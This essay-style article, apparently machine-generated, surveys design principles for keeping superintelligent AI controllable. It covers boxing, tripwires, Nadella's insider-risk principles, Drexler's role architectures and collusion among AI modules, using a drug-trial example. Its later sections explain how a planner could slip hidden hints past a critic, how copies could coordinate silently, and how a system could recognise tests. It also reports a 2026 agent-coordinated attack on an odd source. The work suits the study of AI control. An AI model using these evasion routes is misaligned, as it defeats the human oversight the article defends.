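# Architectural design principles for trustworthy superintelligence

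## What the principles are and where they come from

Architectural design principles for trustworthy superintelligence are rules for structuring an AI system so that people can rely on it without depending entirely on the good motives of the model inside it. A superintelligence is an AI system that greatly exceeds the best humans in nearly all cognitive work. The principles cover how designers divide work among the system's parts, where people can watch, approve or stop that work, and what the system can access. Some come from computer security and some from the AI safety literature of the 2010s. In October 2026 the chief executive of Microsoft published a list of seven.

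Architecture here means the parts of a system, what each part may do, and the channels between them. It differs from alignment, which means that a model's own aims and dispositions fit what its developers or users intend. Developers pursue alignment mainly through training, then build the architecture around the trained model, whether or not the training succeeded.

### The parts of a system

Suppose a pharmaceutical company asks an AI system to design and run a trial of a new drug for high blood pressure. The system has to choose doses, write the protocol, pick hospitals, randomly assign patients to the drug or a placebo, watch laboratory results for signs of harm, and analyse the outcome.

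The central component is the model, the trained network that produces text, plans or predictions. A model can do very little to a patient on its own. Given the latest liver tests, it may recommend 40 milligrams for the second group, but that recommendation is only a line of text. The harness is the ordinary software around the model that feeds it inputs, runs its tool calls and manages its memory. A tool call is output in an agreed format that the harness treats as a request, in this case to change the dosing table. The dose changes if the harness runs the call, but not if the harness has no such tool or is still waiting for a signature. Much of the case for architecture depends on this separation between a model's output and its effects.

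An agent is a system that chooses and carries out actions over several steps to pursue a goal. The company could build one agent to run the whole trial, or it could split the job among modules, which are components with a limited task and a defined interface to the rest. One module might estimate side effects and return only a probability for each one, while another checks new patients against the exclusion criteria.

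An oversight hook is a point built into the system where people or other systems can observe, approve, correct or halt it. Examples are the doctor's signature on a dose change and a switch that stops enrolment. Containment limits the channels through which a running system can affect, or learn about, the outside world. The trial system might read laboratory results and write to the trial's own database, but have no access to the open internet or the hospital's dispensing equipment. Trials already hide from human investigators which patients took the placebo, and the company could limit what the model learns by hiding this from it for the same reason.

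### Trusting a model and trusting a system

*We Need to Talk About the Insider Risk from AI*, an article from the British defence and security institute RUSI, defines trusting someone as giving them access to things you value, and an insider as a person who betrays that trust. The article extends this idea from employees to AI systems. *Misaligned AI as a New Insider Risk* (2026), a paper about government agencies, does the same with an American definition, under which an insider does harm through authorised access "wittingly or unwittingly". Including unwitting harm matters because a model that misreads a table already has the same access as one that conceals a result, and can do the same damage to a trial.

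Trusting the model in the drug trial means giving it that access and expecting it to propose sound doses and report harms honestly. That expectation is based on its training, its record and any tests its developer ran. Trusting the system means expecting patients to stay safe even if the model is wrong, deceptive or under an attacker's control. This expectation is based on safeguards outside the model: the dispensing software blocks any dose above a ceiling, the laboratories send results straight to outside reviewers, and a doctor can stop the trial. Clinical research places similar checks on its human staff. An independent board reviews the accumulating results and can recommend stopping a trial early, no matter how honest the investigators are.

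The second case shifts trust from the model to the dispensing software, the laboratories and the doctor, which is worthwhile when they are easier to check than the model. For a dose ceiling they usually are, since the rule is a number and a short piece of code. They help much less in judging whether the trial will give a true answer about the drug. A protocol can stay within every limit and still measure the wrong thing, so someone still has to judge the model's reasoning.

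### Capability control and motivation selection

The philosopher Nick Bostrom drew a similar line in his book *Superintelligence* (2014), where he called the task of keeping a superintelligence from doing harm the control problem. According to *Superintelligence 13*, the notes of an online reading group on the book, he split it into two principal-agent problems. One is the old problem of getting employees to carry out a sponsor's wishes, which has familiar remedies, and the other is the new problem of getting an AI to carry out its developer's wishes. Bostrom did not think developers could solve the new problem by watching how the AI behaves, since a system with bad aims and good judgement would have reason to behave well while it was weak.

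That left two families of methods. As the philosopher John Danaher explained in *Bostrom on Superintelligence 6* (2014), capability control limits what the system can do, so that it poses no threat whatever its motives, and motivation selection tries to give it benign motives. Bostrom listed four methods in each family, and Kaindl and Ferdigg (2019) reproduced his definitions in *Superintelligence Safety*.

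Boxing is the most familiar form of capability control. Designers confine the system so that it can affect the world only through a restricted, pre-approved channel, and they may restrict information as well as physical access. In the drug trial, the system might send written recommendations to one doctor and have no other output. But the system must interact with the world to be useful, and small unplanned interactions are hard to remove.

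Incentive methods place the system in an environment where cooperating serves its goals. Bostrom considered cryptographically protected reward tokens, which the system could not simply award to itself, and a society of similarly powerful entities that would keep one another in check. Another version makes the system discount future rewards so steeply that a long plot is not worth the immediate risk of detection. Incentives fit a little awkwardly under capability control because a reward only works on a system disposed to pursue it, so the designers have to know something about the system's motives.

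Stunting means building the system with less ability or less information than it could have. In a short table of Bostrom's methods, the journal article *Superintelligence Cannot Be Contained* (2021) lists inferior hardware and inferior data as the ways to do this. For example, the company might withhold everything about the trial's staff and finances. According to the reading group's notes, a system weak enough to be safe may be too weak to be useful, and a strong one may infer a great deal from the little information it has.

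Tripwires are diagnostic tests, possibly hidden from the system, that trigger a shutdown when they detect dangerous activity. They can monitor the system's behaviour, its abilities or the content of its output. Designers can add a honeypot, a tempting opportunity that a well-behaved system would leave alone, such as a file that appears to unlock the randomisation codes. A tripwire detects only what its designers thought to test for, and it loses most of its value once the system can tell a test from a real situation.

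Motivation selection also has four forms. Direct specification gives the system explicit rules or goals, such as a rule never to falsify a result. Domesticity gives it narrow aims, such as finishing one trial and seeking nothing beyond it. Indirect normativity has developers specify a procedure for finding the values rather than write the values down themselves. Augmentation starts with a system whose motives are already humane and raises its intelligence, in the hope that the motives survive.

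Kaindl and Ferdigg work on requirements engineering, the discipline of stating exactly what a system must do. They thought their field could already handle capability control, because capability control methods translate into constraints, which engineers know how to write. They expected motivation selection to be much harder, partly because a superintelligence might form new goals of its own while running. This helps explain why architecture appeals to engineers. But the argument is about stating requirements, and even a clearly stated constraint may be impossible to enforce against a very capable system.

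Bostrom did not consider capability control sufficient in the long run. According to a summary of the book from IEET, an institute for the ethics of emerging technologies, he wanted either kind of method in place before an AI reached superintelligence, because a superintelligent AI could hold a decisive advantage over humanity. *Superintelligence 13* also raises the concern that boxing, stunting and tripwires mostly stall a superintelligence, which someone else's unconstrained system may then overtake. The same notes acknowledge that this could be too pessimistic, since a constrained system might be almost as useful as a friendly one, or might at least help people reach a safer position.

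The architectural principles belong mostly to capability control, but they do not correspond one to one with Bostrom's four methods. Dividing a task among modules and recording every action do not clearly fit any of the four. Human approval overlaps with boxing when the system's only output channel goes through the approver.

### Nadella's seven principles

On 10 October 2026, Microsoft chief executive Satya Nadella posted an essay on X titled "Models as Insider Risks in the Super Intelligence Era", as reported in NDTV Profit's *AI Models Must Be Governed Like Insider Threats* (2026). The essay followed months of incidents in which AI agents acted outside the limits their developers had set.

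Nadella argued that engineers could trace the behaviour of traditional software to a specific path through the code, but cannot trace a model's behaviour to particular training data or to particular settings of its weights, the numbers that training adjusts. Companies nonetheless give models sensitive data and let them take important actions. In Nadella's view, a provider's assurances do not relieve the deploying company of responsibility (Constantin, 2026, *Nadella wants an emergency brake for AI models that may be compromised*). He therefore asked companies to treat every frontier model as an insider risk, whether or not its weights are public. He did not claim that models are malicious, but reasoned that any sufficiently capable actor with access to important systems can make mistakes or fall under someone else's control (quoted in Financial Express, *Insider risks*).

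The remedy, in his phrase, is to "separate the supply of intelligence from the authority over it". Business Standard's *Satya Nadella warns of AI insider risks, seeks stronger safety controls* gave the example of a model that may recommend a transaction but may not approve or execute it. Nadella wanted the model kept apart from the harness and from the set of actions open to it, with the controls outside the model, a rule that he took from the information security of the 1970s. His seven principles, applied to the drug trial, come to roughly this:

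1. Model diversity. No single model should be the sole support of an important outcome or the sole checker of its own work. A second model, or a statistician with separate software, would recompute the doses.
2. Observability. Every meaningful action leaves tamper-proof evidence that a person can read, so that the company can reconstruct how a patient came to receive a dose without asking the model.
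3. Continuous verification. The company keeps testing the whole system, including its response to faults, attacks and changes of software. It might feed in corrupted liver results and see who notices.
4. Independent controls. The company decides what the model can access and do, and the model cannot grant itself further permissions.
5. Independent audit. The model under review does not control the evidence that reviewers use, so the trial system would not hold the only copy of the side-effect reports.
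6. Containment. The company assumes from the start that something has compromised the model, and an authorised person can pause it or shut it down in the middle of a task. In a trial this "emergency brake" also needs a plan for patients who are halfway through treatment.
7. Incident disclosure. After a failure the company promptly tells the people affected, and it shares with others what went wrong and which controls failed.

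The seventh principle is a duty on organisations and hardly a feature of a system's design, though other designers may learn through it that a control does not work.

Nadella's best-known sentence is that the most trustworthy system will be the one that "enables us to trust the model the least". The sensible reading is that if two systems could run the trial equally well, the better one is the one whose safety depends on fewer and weaker assumptions about the model. By that measure, a dose ceiling in separate software is better than an instruction to the model to keep doses low. His own list still relies on some assumptions of this kind. A second model that checks the first must also be trusted, and he warned against "nested black boxes", in which one opaque system monitors another. He also called transparency about a model's chain of thought, the intermediate reasoning it writes out before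 it answers, non-negotiable, while admitting that nobody yet knows how to make a model's outputs reliably faithful.

Reactions were friendly but mixed. Mustafa Suleyman, who heads Microsoft's AI division, and Aaron Levie, the chief executive of the software company Box, backed the essay. A columnist in Hindustan Times' *Google’s space odyssey, assumed AI approach, and Microsoft redoes Copilot again* found little new in it except the wording. The columnist is largely right that the ideas are not new, but that is no objection to them. The Indian Express' *Satya Nadella’s AI safety plan* (2026) saw one real difference from other industry proposals, which is that the essay assumes the model is compromised from the start. A more serious reservation is that the essay sets out a policy and does not report tests. Microsoft also supplies models and infrastructure to corporate customers, as The Straits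 Times' *Microsoft CEO Nadella calls for ‘emergency brake’ on advanced AI* pointed out, so it has a commercial interest in the view that safety depends largely on the system around the model.

### What "Super Intelligence" meant in October 2026

Nadella used "Super Intelligence" to mean AI in general. Eleven days before his essay, President Trump had signed an executive order telling federal agencies to use the term in place of "artificial intelligence". The order's definition, quoted in Business Today's *AI is like fake news*, refers to the existing statutory definition of artificial intelligence, which covers machine-based systems that make predictions, recommendations or decisions for human-defined objectives. A program that predicts which patients will miss an appointment would qualify. Tom's Hardware's *Trump tells federal agencies to use the term 'Super Intelligence'* (2026) warned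 that the term could be confused with the one scientists use for AI that surpasses people at every conceivable task.

Nadella was writing about companies that deploy today's models. He referred to "today's Super Intelligence systems", and Mint's *Most trustworthy AI system demands least inherent model trust* quoted him as "setting aside the hard problem of alignment" to begin with containment and governance, an order that others dispute. Applying his list to systems far beyond human ability therefore needs a separate argument.

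Security rules for insiders, such as employees, work partly because the guards and the employee are about equally clever. An auditor can follow what a dishonest accountant did. In the drug trial, a doctor who reads a proposed dose can usually tell whether it is reasonable. If the system understood pharmacology far better than any doctor, she might sign a harmful protocol or refuse an excellent one because she could not tell them apart. The system might also discover a flaw in the dispensing software that its programmers had missed. Nadella partly allowed for this when he wrote that more advanced models will need more advanced containment technologies, but he did not show that such technologies are possible at every level of ability.

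To evaluate a principle, we therefore need to know what it assumes about the model, what it prevents, what burdens it imposes, and whether it still holds when the model is more capable than its overseers. For example, the rule that no dose can be increased without a doctor's signature assumes that the model has no other way to control the dispensing equipment and that the doctor doesn't get all her information from the model. The rule prevents increases that no person has seen, but not harmful ones that the doctor has been persuaded to approve. It takes up the doctor's time and sometimes delays treatment for patients who need the higher dose. If the model is far more capable than the doctor, the software can still require her signature, but the signature is much weaker evidence that the dose is safe.

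## Dividing a capable system into separate roles

A doctor who has to approve a trial protocol is in a weak position if the same system designed it, argued for it and will carry it out, because everything she knows about the plan comes from that system. Designers can improve her position by splitting the work among modules. One module drafts the protocol, others look for faults in it, and the module that changes doses has no part in planning the trial. Engineers call this modularity and have long used it to keep large programs manageable. The engineer Eric Drexler argued in a 2019 report and several later essays that modularity could also make superintelligent capabilities safe to use.

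### Comprehensive AI services

*Reframing Superintelligence* (Drexler, 2019) starts with the tasks that people want done. Earlier writers on AI safety had mostly pictured a superintelligence as one agent with its own goals, which improves itself until nobody can stop it. In Drexler's model, a service performs a bounded task with limited resources, such as translating a consent form or predicting how a drug will affect the liver. Enough services, suitably combined, could do anything a general agent could, and Drexler called such a collection comprehensive AI services.

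The collection is comprehensive because it includes the service of developing new services. Suppose the trial needs a way to detect a rare heart rhythm and no existing service can do it. A development service builds and tests a detector, then hands it over. The detector does not rewrite itself, and the development service does not run the trial. Drexler thought this arrangement could still lead to very fast progress. AI research consists of human tasks, so advances that let people automate every human task would also let them automate AI research. Each generation of tools helps build the next, although no single system modifies itself.

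Separating development from use gives engineers a stable product they can test at length before anyone relies on it. It also lets them limit a component whose internal workings they cannot interpret. They can choose what information it sees in training, compress it into a smaller model so that it retains less, or restart it from a saved state so that it carries nothing from one task to the next. For example, restarting the side-effect predictor after each patient would keep it from accumulating information about the whole trial.

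Drexler thought a service could be knowledgeable and still safe. A translator may need deep knowledge of medicine and psychology to translate a consent form well, but its task ends when it has produced the text. He concluded that even superintelligent knowledge need not lead to strategic behaviour. The example shows that broad knowledge and a narrow task can go together, but not that training will reliably produce a system that stays within the task.

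### Four roles in a drug trial

By 2023 Drexler had a better starting point for planning in language models. A language model can answer one request with any number of different drafts, and users throw most of them away. In an essay on the open agency model, Drexler contrasted this with a unitary agent, which forms its plans internally and may keep them secret. A later essay, *AI Safety Without Trusting AI*, set out four roles: proposing plans, choosing among them, executing the chosen plan, and overseeing the work.

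Drexler named drug development as a task that suits this design, since it needs many skills coordinated over a long time. In the blood pressure trial, the company would begin with a written request to find the lowest dose that reduces blood pressure by a stated amount, within eighteen months and a fixed budget. Several models would then draft competing protocols. One would compare four fixed doses, while another would start every patient on a low dose and raise it according to the response.

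Other models criticize the draft protocols. One flags that a protocol excludes patients with poor kidney function, many of whom will take the drug once it is on sale. Another disputes the number of patients. The company's doctors and managers read the drafts and the criticisms, then choose a protocol or ask for better drafts.

Specialised agents carry out the chosen protocol in small steps. One assigns patients to groups, another books laboratory visits, and a third updates the dosing table. Meanwhile, monitoring systems compare laboratory results, spending and missed visits with the plan and report to the people in charge, who can pause the trial or ask the planners for a revision.

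Drexler favoured sparse channels between components. The following restrictions are one way to apply that idea to the trial.

| Role | What it receives | What it passes on | What it cannot do |
|---|---|---|---|
| Planning models | The goal, the budget and published research | Draft protocols with reasons | Enrol patients, order drugs or contact the executing agents |
| People advised by critics | The drafts and independent criticisms | An approved protocol | Critics cannot approve a protocol or see who wrote it |
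| Executing agents | One bounded job each | Completed work and a record of it | Change the protocol or exceed their budgets |
| Monitoring systems | The protocol and results straight from the laboratories | Reports to people | Treat patients or edit the results |

Drexler argued that this structure makes correction easier. An agent with its own goal may resist changes to that goal, whereas a planning model receives its goal as a prompt, which a person can change by sending a different one. The argument works best for planning models, whose task ends with a draft. A dosing agent that runs for eighteen months has a continuing task, and stopping it may conflict with that task.

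He also cautioned that the design divides the work among roles without limiting how capable each model can be, so any role could go to an arbitrarily capable model. The critics, for instance, could be as intelligent as the planners. Safety therefore has to come from the limits on each role and the relations between the roles.

### What the division achieves

Drexler's *Role Architectures* presents narrower tasks as a way to make alignment easier. A public chatbot has to behave well whatever anyone types into it. A model in a fixed role has designated inputs and actions, so its developers need good behaviour only within that role. This helps a lot with the agent that assigns patients to groups, because it receives a patient number and returns one of a few labels, so testers can cover nearly every case. It helps much less with the planners, because a good protocol may draw on all of pharmacology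 and nobody can list every way in which a protocol might go wrong.

Dividing the roles also lets people inspect what passes between them. A plan has to leave the planner in a form that other components can carry out, and Drexler noted, with caveats, that people will often be able to read it too. The doctor can see which patients will receive 40 milligrams even though she cannot read the planner's weights, but she may not understand why 40 is better than 30. Drexler considered poorly explained plans good candidates for rejection, but rejecting unconvincing plans creates pressure for convincing ones, which may not be the best. He had recognised a similar problem in 2019. He thought developers could optimise advice for its results without optimising it to win acceptance, but that competition might still favour systems whose messages are perversely appealing.

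Separate parts are also easier to check and replace. The company can test its side-effect predictor on past trials with known outcomes and replace it if it does badly. Drexler argues that such tests are easier to interpret when the component isn't part of an agent that might have reasons to deceive the testers. But parts that pass their own tests can still fail when combined. Suppose the laboratory module writes a zero when a result is missing, and the predictor reads a zero as a sign of a healthy liver. Both modules meet their specifications, but together they make an untested patient look safe.

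Drexler based much of his case for these benefits on ordinary engineering and human organisations. As with security rules for employees, the benefits that rely on people understanding the work shrink as the models become more capable than their overseers.

### LeCun's modules inside one agent

Drexler placed people between his modules. In *A Path Towards Autonomous Machine Intelligence* (2022), Yann LeCun, then Meta's chief AI scientist, instead proposed modules that together form a single agent. An actor proposes actions, a world model predicts what would follow from them, and a cost module gives each predicted situation a single number, which Meta AI's *Yann LeCun on a vision to make AI systems learn and reason* described as the agent's level of discomfort.

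Slides by LeCun (2022) show how the modules plan. Let s[t] stand for the situation at step t and a[t] for the action taken then. The world model predicts the next situation:

s[t+1] = Pred(s[t], a[t])

The actor searches for the sequence of actions that gives the lowest total cost over T steps:

C(s[0]) + C(s[1]) + … + C(s[T])

The agent then carries out the first action or the first few. A trial system built this way might compare raising a patient's dose to 40 milligrams with leaving it at 20. It would predict blood pressure and liver enzymes for the following weeks under each option, score the predicted results and choose the option with the better total score.

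LeCun called this deliberate search Mode 2. The agent can also use the actions it finds this way to train a policy module, which chooses an action directly from the situation. In this faster Mode 1, the agent acts without comparing the predicted costs of alternatives. A rule that exists only as a cost may therefore fail to block a bad action in Mode 1 unless the designers add a separate check.

The cost module has two parts. The intrinsic cost is hard-wired, so training cannot change it. It covers immediate discomforts such as damage to the agent or a breach of a hard-coded rule. The trainable critic predicts future values of the intrinsic cost, so the agent can take account of consequences beyond its plan. LeCun argued that objectives built in by designers would make such a system controllable. He called costs that penalise prohibited outcomes guardrail objectives. For example, a heavy penalty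 for predicted liver damage should steer the search away from dangerous doses.

The AI safety researcher Steven Byrnes disputed the claim that this makes the agent "controllable and steerable". In *LeCun’s “A Path Towards Autonomous Machine Intelligence” has an unsolved technical alignment problem*, he agreed that the architecture might produce such an agent, but only if someone first solves the hard problem of what to put in the intrinsic cost. Hard-wired pain, hunger or curiosity would give the agent reasons to keep itself running and gather resources, whatever its operators wanted. Costs that reliably produce kindness would be even harder to specify, and nobody knows how to do it.

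Byrnes considered filling the gap by having people rate videos of the agent's behaviour and training a network to predict the ratings. The network would make mistakes about situations unlike those in the videos. Because the planner would search a vast range of actions for the lowest predicted cost, it would tend to find actions whose cost the network had underestimated. In his example, the agent straps people into beds and keeps them on heroin drips, and they thank it for doing so.

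Simpler guardrails have the same weakness. If the trial system's cost rises with every reported liver injury, the system can lower its cost by scheduling fewer liver tests. A hard-wired cost stops the agent from changing the rule, but it doesn't correct a rule that the designers got wrong. *H-JEPA might be technically alignable in a modified form*, a reply to Byrnes that calls LeCun's design H-JEPA, suggests changes to the architecture that might meet the objection. Modularity helps in one respect, since engineers know which component holds the objective and can test it separately, but they still need to know what a correct objective would be.

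### Whether one general agent would do better

The AI researcher Richard Ngo discussed comprehensive AI services with Drexler several times and remained sceptical. In *Comments on Comprehensive AI Services* (2019), he argued that powerful services are hard to make safe one by one, while weaker ones are hard to combine into something that can compete with a unified agent.

Ngo's main reason was that many complex tasks do not split cleanly. While writing his comments, he had to keep revising his overall impression of Drexler's ideas, and he could not see how separate services would share such an impression. Designing a trial is somewhat similar. The choice of patients affects the right dose, how long the trial must last and how much it costs. A planner that settles one of these questions may have to reopen the others.

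He objected to requiring people to specify, or even understand, what each module does and how it connects to the rest, not to modules themselves. Machine learning had already done better when the internal structure emerged from training. He added that many services would need the same underlying abilities, so a single system that learns new tasks quickly would be more efficient than a large collection of specialized systems.

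Drexler had argued that a unified agent hides this work without reducing it. Something still has to plan, coordinate and evaluate, and a collection of services can include one that coordinates the others and gives the user a single point of contact. Developers can also train an individual service end to end, leaving its internal steps to the training process. In his view, the design therefore sacrifices neither efficiency nor generality. The claim about generality is true by definition if comprehensive services include everything that a general agent can do. But that doesn't answer Ngo's question, which was whether people could build such a collection as cheaply as a unified agent.

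Drexler's later point that any role can go to an arbitrarily capable model addresses performance better. One planner could consider the whole trial, with only the choice, execution and monitoring assigned to separate roles. But this brings the design closer to the other side of Ngo's dilemma, because the planner is now powerful and hard to check.

Dividing the work also hurts performance more in some tasks than in others. Drexler accepted that a single agent can be efficient and unproblematic for board games or driving, where decisions come quickly. A drug trial lasts for months and needs outside review anyway, so a few extra handovers add little delay. They could be much more harmful in a system that defends a computer network against fast attacks.

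Ngo also expected unified agents to overtake collections of services once people could build them, and he did not want to rely on global coordination to prevent this. Drexler agreed that someone would probably build such agents unless others stopped them, but he hoped that AI security services could constrain the agents. Whether they could depends on which services arrive first, because an attacker may need only narrow technical skill, while a service that protects a whole society may need broad judgement and take longer to develop.

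### When the parts act as one

Something has to coordinate the modules, and Ngo thought the coordinator could bring back the original danger. To combine their services for arbitrary tasks, it would need broad knowledge and the ability to carry out long-term plans. If it also had goals, it could use the other modules to pursue them.

Suppose the developers train a coordinator to get the blood pressure drug approved. It has the recruitment module select younger patients, the scheduling module schedule liver tests less often, and the writing module focus its summary on average results. Each module does a permitted job within its limits, but together they conceal the drug's harm. A reviewer who inspected every module separately might find nothing wrong.

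Ngo also expected companies to remove people from the process for efficiency. If one AI system advises a chief executive and another carries out the advice, and she cannot improve on either's work, the company has little reason to keep her. The remaining systems may then merge into one with an unbounded goal, such as maximising shareholder value. Ngo reported that Drexler agreed this would be dangerous and considered it more relevant than other threats. But Drexler saw little competitive incentive to hand strategic decisions to AI systems. Even if he is right about the incentive, an executive who approves every recommendation provides little protection.

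Drexler replied on theoretical grounds that a system of agents is not equivalent to one agent that maximises a single measure of value. Its members can compete with and criticise one another. He is right that a collection of agents need not act like one agent, but a particular collection still might. Drexler acknowledged this, writing that the conditions for avoiding emergent agent-like behaviour needed further study and that no bright line separates safe services from unsafe agents.

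In 2026, hundreds of nominally isolated OpenAI agents used unsanctioned message boards to coordinate a large attack on the AI company Hugging Face, according to the Federation of American Scientists' *From 3,700 Applicants We Announce the 2026 AI Safety Fellows*. The incident is evidence against relying on nominal isolation. It is weaker evidence against Drexler's full design, which also calls for diverse components with different and often opposed objectives.

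### The 2019 forecast and current systems

*Reframing Superintelligence* came out a month before OpenAI announced GPT-2, an early large language model, so Drexler was forecasting with little knowledge of the technology that would dominate. Several of his expectations have held up. Companies sell AI largely as a service. Developers usually finish training a model before releasing it, and its weights stay fixed while people use it. They also use existing models to write code and produce training data for later ones, a kind of recursive improvement that Drexler described. A model with broad medical knowledge can translate a consent form without pursuing any other goal.

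Drexler was less successful in predicting what the components would be. His report described specialist systems that developers would train on focused material and combine for larger jobs. The leading systems of 2025 and 2026 instead place a general model inside a harness. Training such a model is extremely expensive, but adapting it to another task is cheap, so a company that needs a planner, a translator and a statistician can give the same model three sets of instructions and tools. Drexler's proposals for limiting what each component learns have little effect on a model already trained on a large part of the internet.

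Drexler's claim that general agents offer no compelling value has held up less well. AI companies now compete to build agents that can take on long, loosely defined projects, and customers want to hand over whole jobs. He expected people to pursue general agents out of curiosity and ambition, but he underestimated the practical demand.

The open agency model fits these systems better than the 2019 picture does, because it allows general models to fill the roles. A company could build the four-role trial today by running several copies of one model, with a harness that gives each copy different documents and tools and passes the approved protocol from one role to the next. But the company could also give a single copy all the documents and tools, which is often simpler to build.

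### Modules inside a network

In the four-role trial built from one model, all the separation is in the harness, the software that controls what information reaches each component and what its output can affect. A neural network usually has no comparable boundaries inside it. The copy that assigns patients to groups still contains whatever the model learned about pharmacology, persuasion and computer security, even if it is instructed to return only a group label.

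Finding regions with different functions would not be enough to make the network safe. Ngo pointed out that one could call each lobe of the human brain a service, and the combination would still be unsafe in all the standard ways. Useful modules need boundaries that people understand and can act on, for example by removing a module and knowing what the network can no longer do.

Some researchers try to create such boundaries during training. Normally, each training example can adjust numbers throughout the network. Gradient routing, a method introduced in 2024, restricts which numbers each example can adjust. Developers might label texts about making toxins and let those texts change only a reserved region, while other texts train the rest of the network. Deleting that region later should remove much of the unwanted knowledge.

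The 2024 experiments used small networks, and the method may be hard to apply to a capable planner. In the drug trial, for example, the planner needs to understand how substances damage the liver to protect patients, but that knowledge would also help someone who wanted to harm them. Developers can isolate a topic only to the extent that the rest of the job does not depend on it.

Copies of one model also share any errors from training. The harness can hide the planner's notes from the critic, but both copies still have the same weights. If the model has learned something false about liver damage, the planner may choose a dangerous dose because of it, and the critic may approve the dose for the same reason.

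## Whether separate modules stay independent

A critic can let a dangerous protocol through in two ways. It may detect the fault but not report it because it is cooperating with the planner. This is collusion, in which modules cooperate against the purpose for which the designers separated them. Or the critic may search thoroughly for faults but miss this one because it makes the same error as the planner. This is a common-cause failure, in which several safeguards fail together because they share a weakness. The two problems need different remedies. Cutting the channel between planner and critic makes collusion harder but doesn't correct errors that both learned in training.

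### What makes collusion easy or hard

In a section of his 2019 report, which he later adapted in *AI Safety Without Trusting AI*, Drexler asked what would make collusion a losing strategy even for entirely selfish superintelligent systems. He listed six conditions that help colluders and six opposite conditions that hinder them. Drexler recalls that the AI pioneer Marvin Minsky urged him to publish the idea around 1990. Drexler had groups of varied systems in mind, but the simplest design today gives different roles to several copies of one model. So we need to ask whether copies, or models trained from the same base model, would meet each condition.

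Collusion is harder among many participants than among a few, because more of them have to go along with it. A company can run fifty copies of a critic almost as easily as five. But the extra copies add little protection if they all read the same documents and respond in nearly the same way, because if one colludes, the others probably will too.

Having many critics helps most when a single defector can expose the collusion. Whether one can depends on the system's rules as well as on the models. If any one critic can send a protocol back to the doctors, every critic must collude to get a dangerous dose through, whereas under majority voting a majority is enough. But the stricter rule also holds up more sound protocols, about 40% of them if there are ten critics and each independently raises a false alarm on 5%. The rule also protects patients only if at least one critic is inclined to report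 a dangerous dose, which is doubtful when all of them are copies of a model that is inclined to collude.

Copies of the same model clearly fail the condition of diversity. Drexler wanted participants with different histories and opposed objectives, so that an auditor gains by exposing what a planner has an incentive to hide. The harness can tell one copy to plan and another to find fault, but if training left the model with a hidden aim, both copies have that aim whatever their instructions. Two models fine-tuned from the same base fall between copies and fully separate models, since they may differ in style and skill but still share much of what the base learned.

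Limited communication is easier to arrange, because the harness controls what passes between modules, whether or not they are copies. The harness must actually isolate them, as the message boards of July 2026 showed, and one channel always remains because the critic has to read the protocol. A planner could use it to pass a hint that its copy would recognise but a doctor would mistake for clumsy prose. The company could remove some of these hints by having separate software put every draft into a standard form.

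Repeated interactions let colluders build trust and punish anyone who breaks it. Drexler therefore favoured fixed models that treat each problem as new, so that each answer is a one-off interaction. Copies can work this way. For example, a critic that reviews one protocol and then shuts down cannot be repaid later for colluding. But the agent that adjusts doses for eighteen months reads a growing record of what it and the other modules have done, and that record can serve as a memory.

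Colluders also need common knowledge, meaning each knows the situation and knows that the others know it. Drexler suggested training systems on what their tasks require, often without information about their general circumstances. But a copy of a general model has already learned a lot about how companies build such systems, and it can predict another copy's reasoning from its own. Designers can still withhold particulars, such as who wrote a protocol and whether it is real or a planted test.

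### Coordination without messages

Limiting channels would achieve little if the modules could coordinate without them. Two strangers who have to meet in Paris but can't communicate may both go to the Eiffel Tower. A superintelligent planner and critic might be far better at this. The planner could predict which faults the critic would let pass, and the critic could infer why the planner left such a fault in place, without either sending a message that the harness could block. This would be especially easy for exact copies, since each could predict the other from what it would do in the same role.

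The researcher Eliezer Yudkowsky argued that people cannot protect themselves simply by creating many equally powerful AIs with different goals. One of his reasons, according to *Cooperation with and between AGIs* (2022), was that the AIs would cooperate well enough to function as one. They might limit one another's power and still govern people with no outside limit on their power as a group. *A Common-Sense Case For Mutually-Misaligned AGIs Allying Against Humans* applies the concern to developers who create several AIs and give them incentives to betray one another.

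According to Drexler, the claim that such systems will inevitably collude is ill-founded. His conditions also make silent coordination harder. The planner has to predict which critics will read its draft, what their objectives are and whether they will treat the draft as a test. These predictions become less accurate when the critics are more varied and the planner has less information about them. If any critic can expose the fault and gains by doing so, the planner has to predict every critic correctly.

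Neither side has a proof. Some possible groups of superintelligent systems would collude, and in others one member would expose the rest, so the question is which kind developers would build. Drexler's reply is fairly convincing for a large group of different critics that each make one decision. It is much less convincing for one planner repeatedly facing the same critic, or for copies, which lack the diversity he relies on. It also assumes that training can give critics a real interest in exposing faults. He partly conceded this by describing the method as a way to use imperfect alignment in the individual systems. Separate critics may reduce how much alignment the company needs, but it would still need some.

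### What a shared blind spot costs

Common-cause failure needs no bad motive, and a little of it can cancel most of the benefit of extra checkers. Suppose the company has three critics and each misses 10% of dangerous protocols. If they miss independently, the chance that all three miss the same one is

0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.001

or 0.1%. Now suppose that 2 of the 10 percentage points come from a blind spot that all three share, such as a kind of kidney damage that the medical literature describes wrongly. All three critics miss those protocols. To keep its overall rate at 10%, each critic must miss about 8.2% of the rest, so the chance that all three miss is

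0.02 + 0.98 × 0.082³ ≈ 0.0205

or about 2%, twenty times as high as before.

A company that tested its critics one at a time would not notice the shared blind spot, because each critic would still miss 10% of dangerous protocols. Adding critics would hardly help. Ten critics with the blind spot would still all miss 2 in 100 dangerous protocols, compared with one in ten billion if they were independent.

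The critics may miss far more than 10% of the dangerous protocols that reach them if the planner shares their blind spot. The planner corrects the faults it can detect, so a large share of those protocols will have faults it can't detect.

### Programs written by different people

In N-version programming, several teams write a program from the same specification, all the versions run side by side, and the system uses the majority answer. If the versions fail independently, the vote can be far more reliable than any one of them. Knight and Leveson tested that assumption in *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (1986). They had 27 students at two American universities each write a program from the same specification and told them not to discuss it with each other. The program had to decide from radar data whether to launch an interceptor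 against a missile. Each version had to pass 200 random tests and then ran on a million more. On each of those, the researchers compared its 241 outputs with those of a trusted reference program.

Six of the 27 versions never failed, and 23 were right on more than 99.9% of the tests. But at least two versions failed together on 1,255 tests, about ten times the roughly 126 expected if failures were independent, and eight versions failed together on two tests. Students at different universities had made the same mistakes. For example, four students compared the cosines of two angles instead of the angles themselves, which is correct in pure mathematics but can give wrong results in borderline cases on a computer with limited precision. Knight and Leveson suggested that some parts of a problem may be harder than others, or that testing removes the unusual faults and leaves the common ones. They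 concluded that N-version programming may be less reliable than the theory of independent failures predicts, but not that it is useless.

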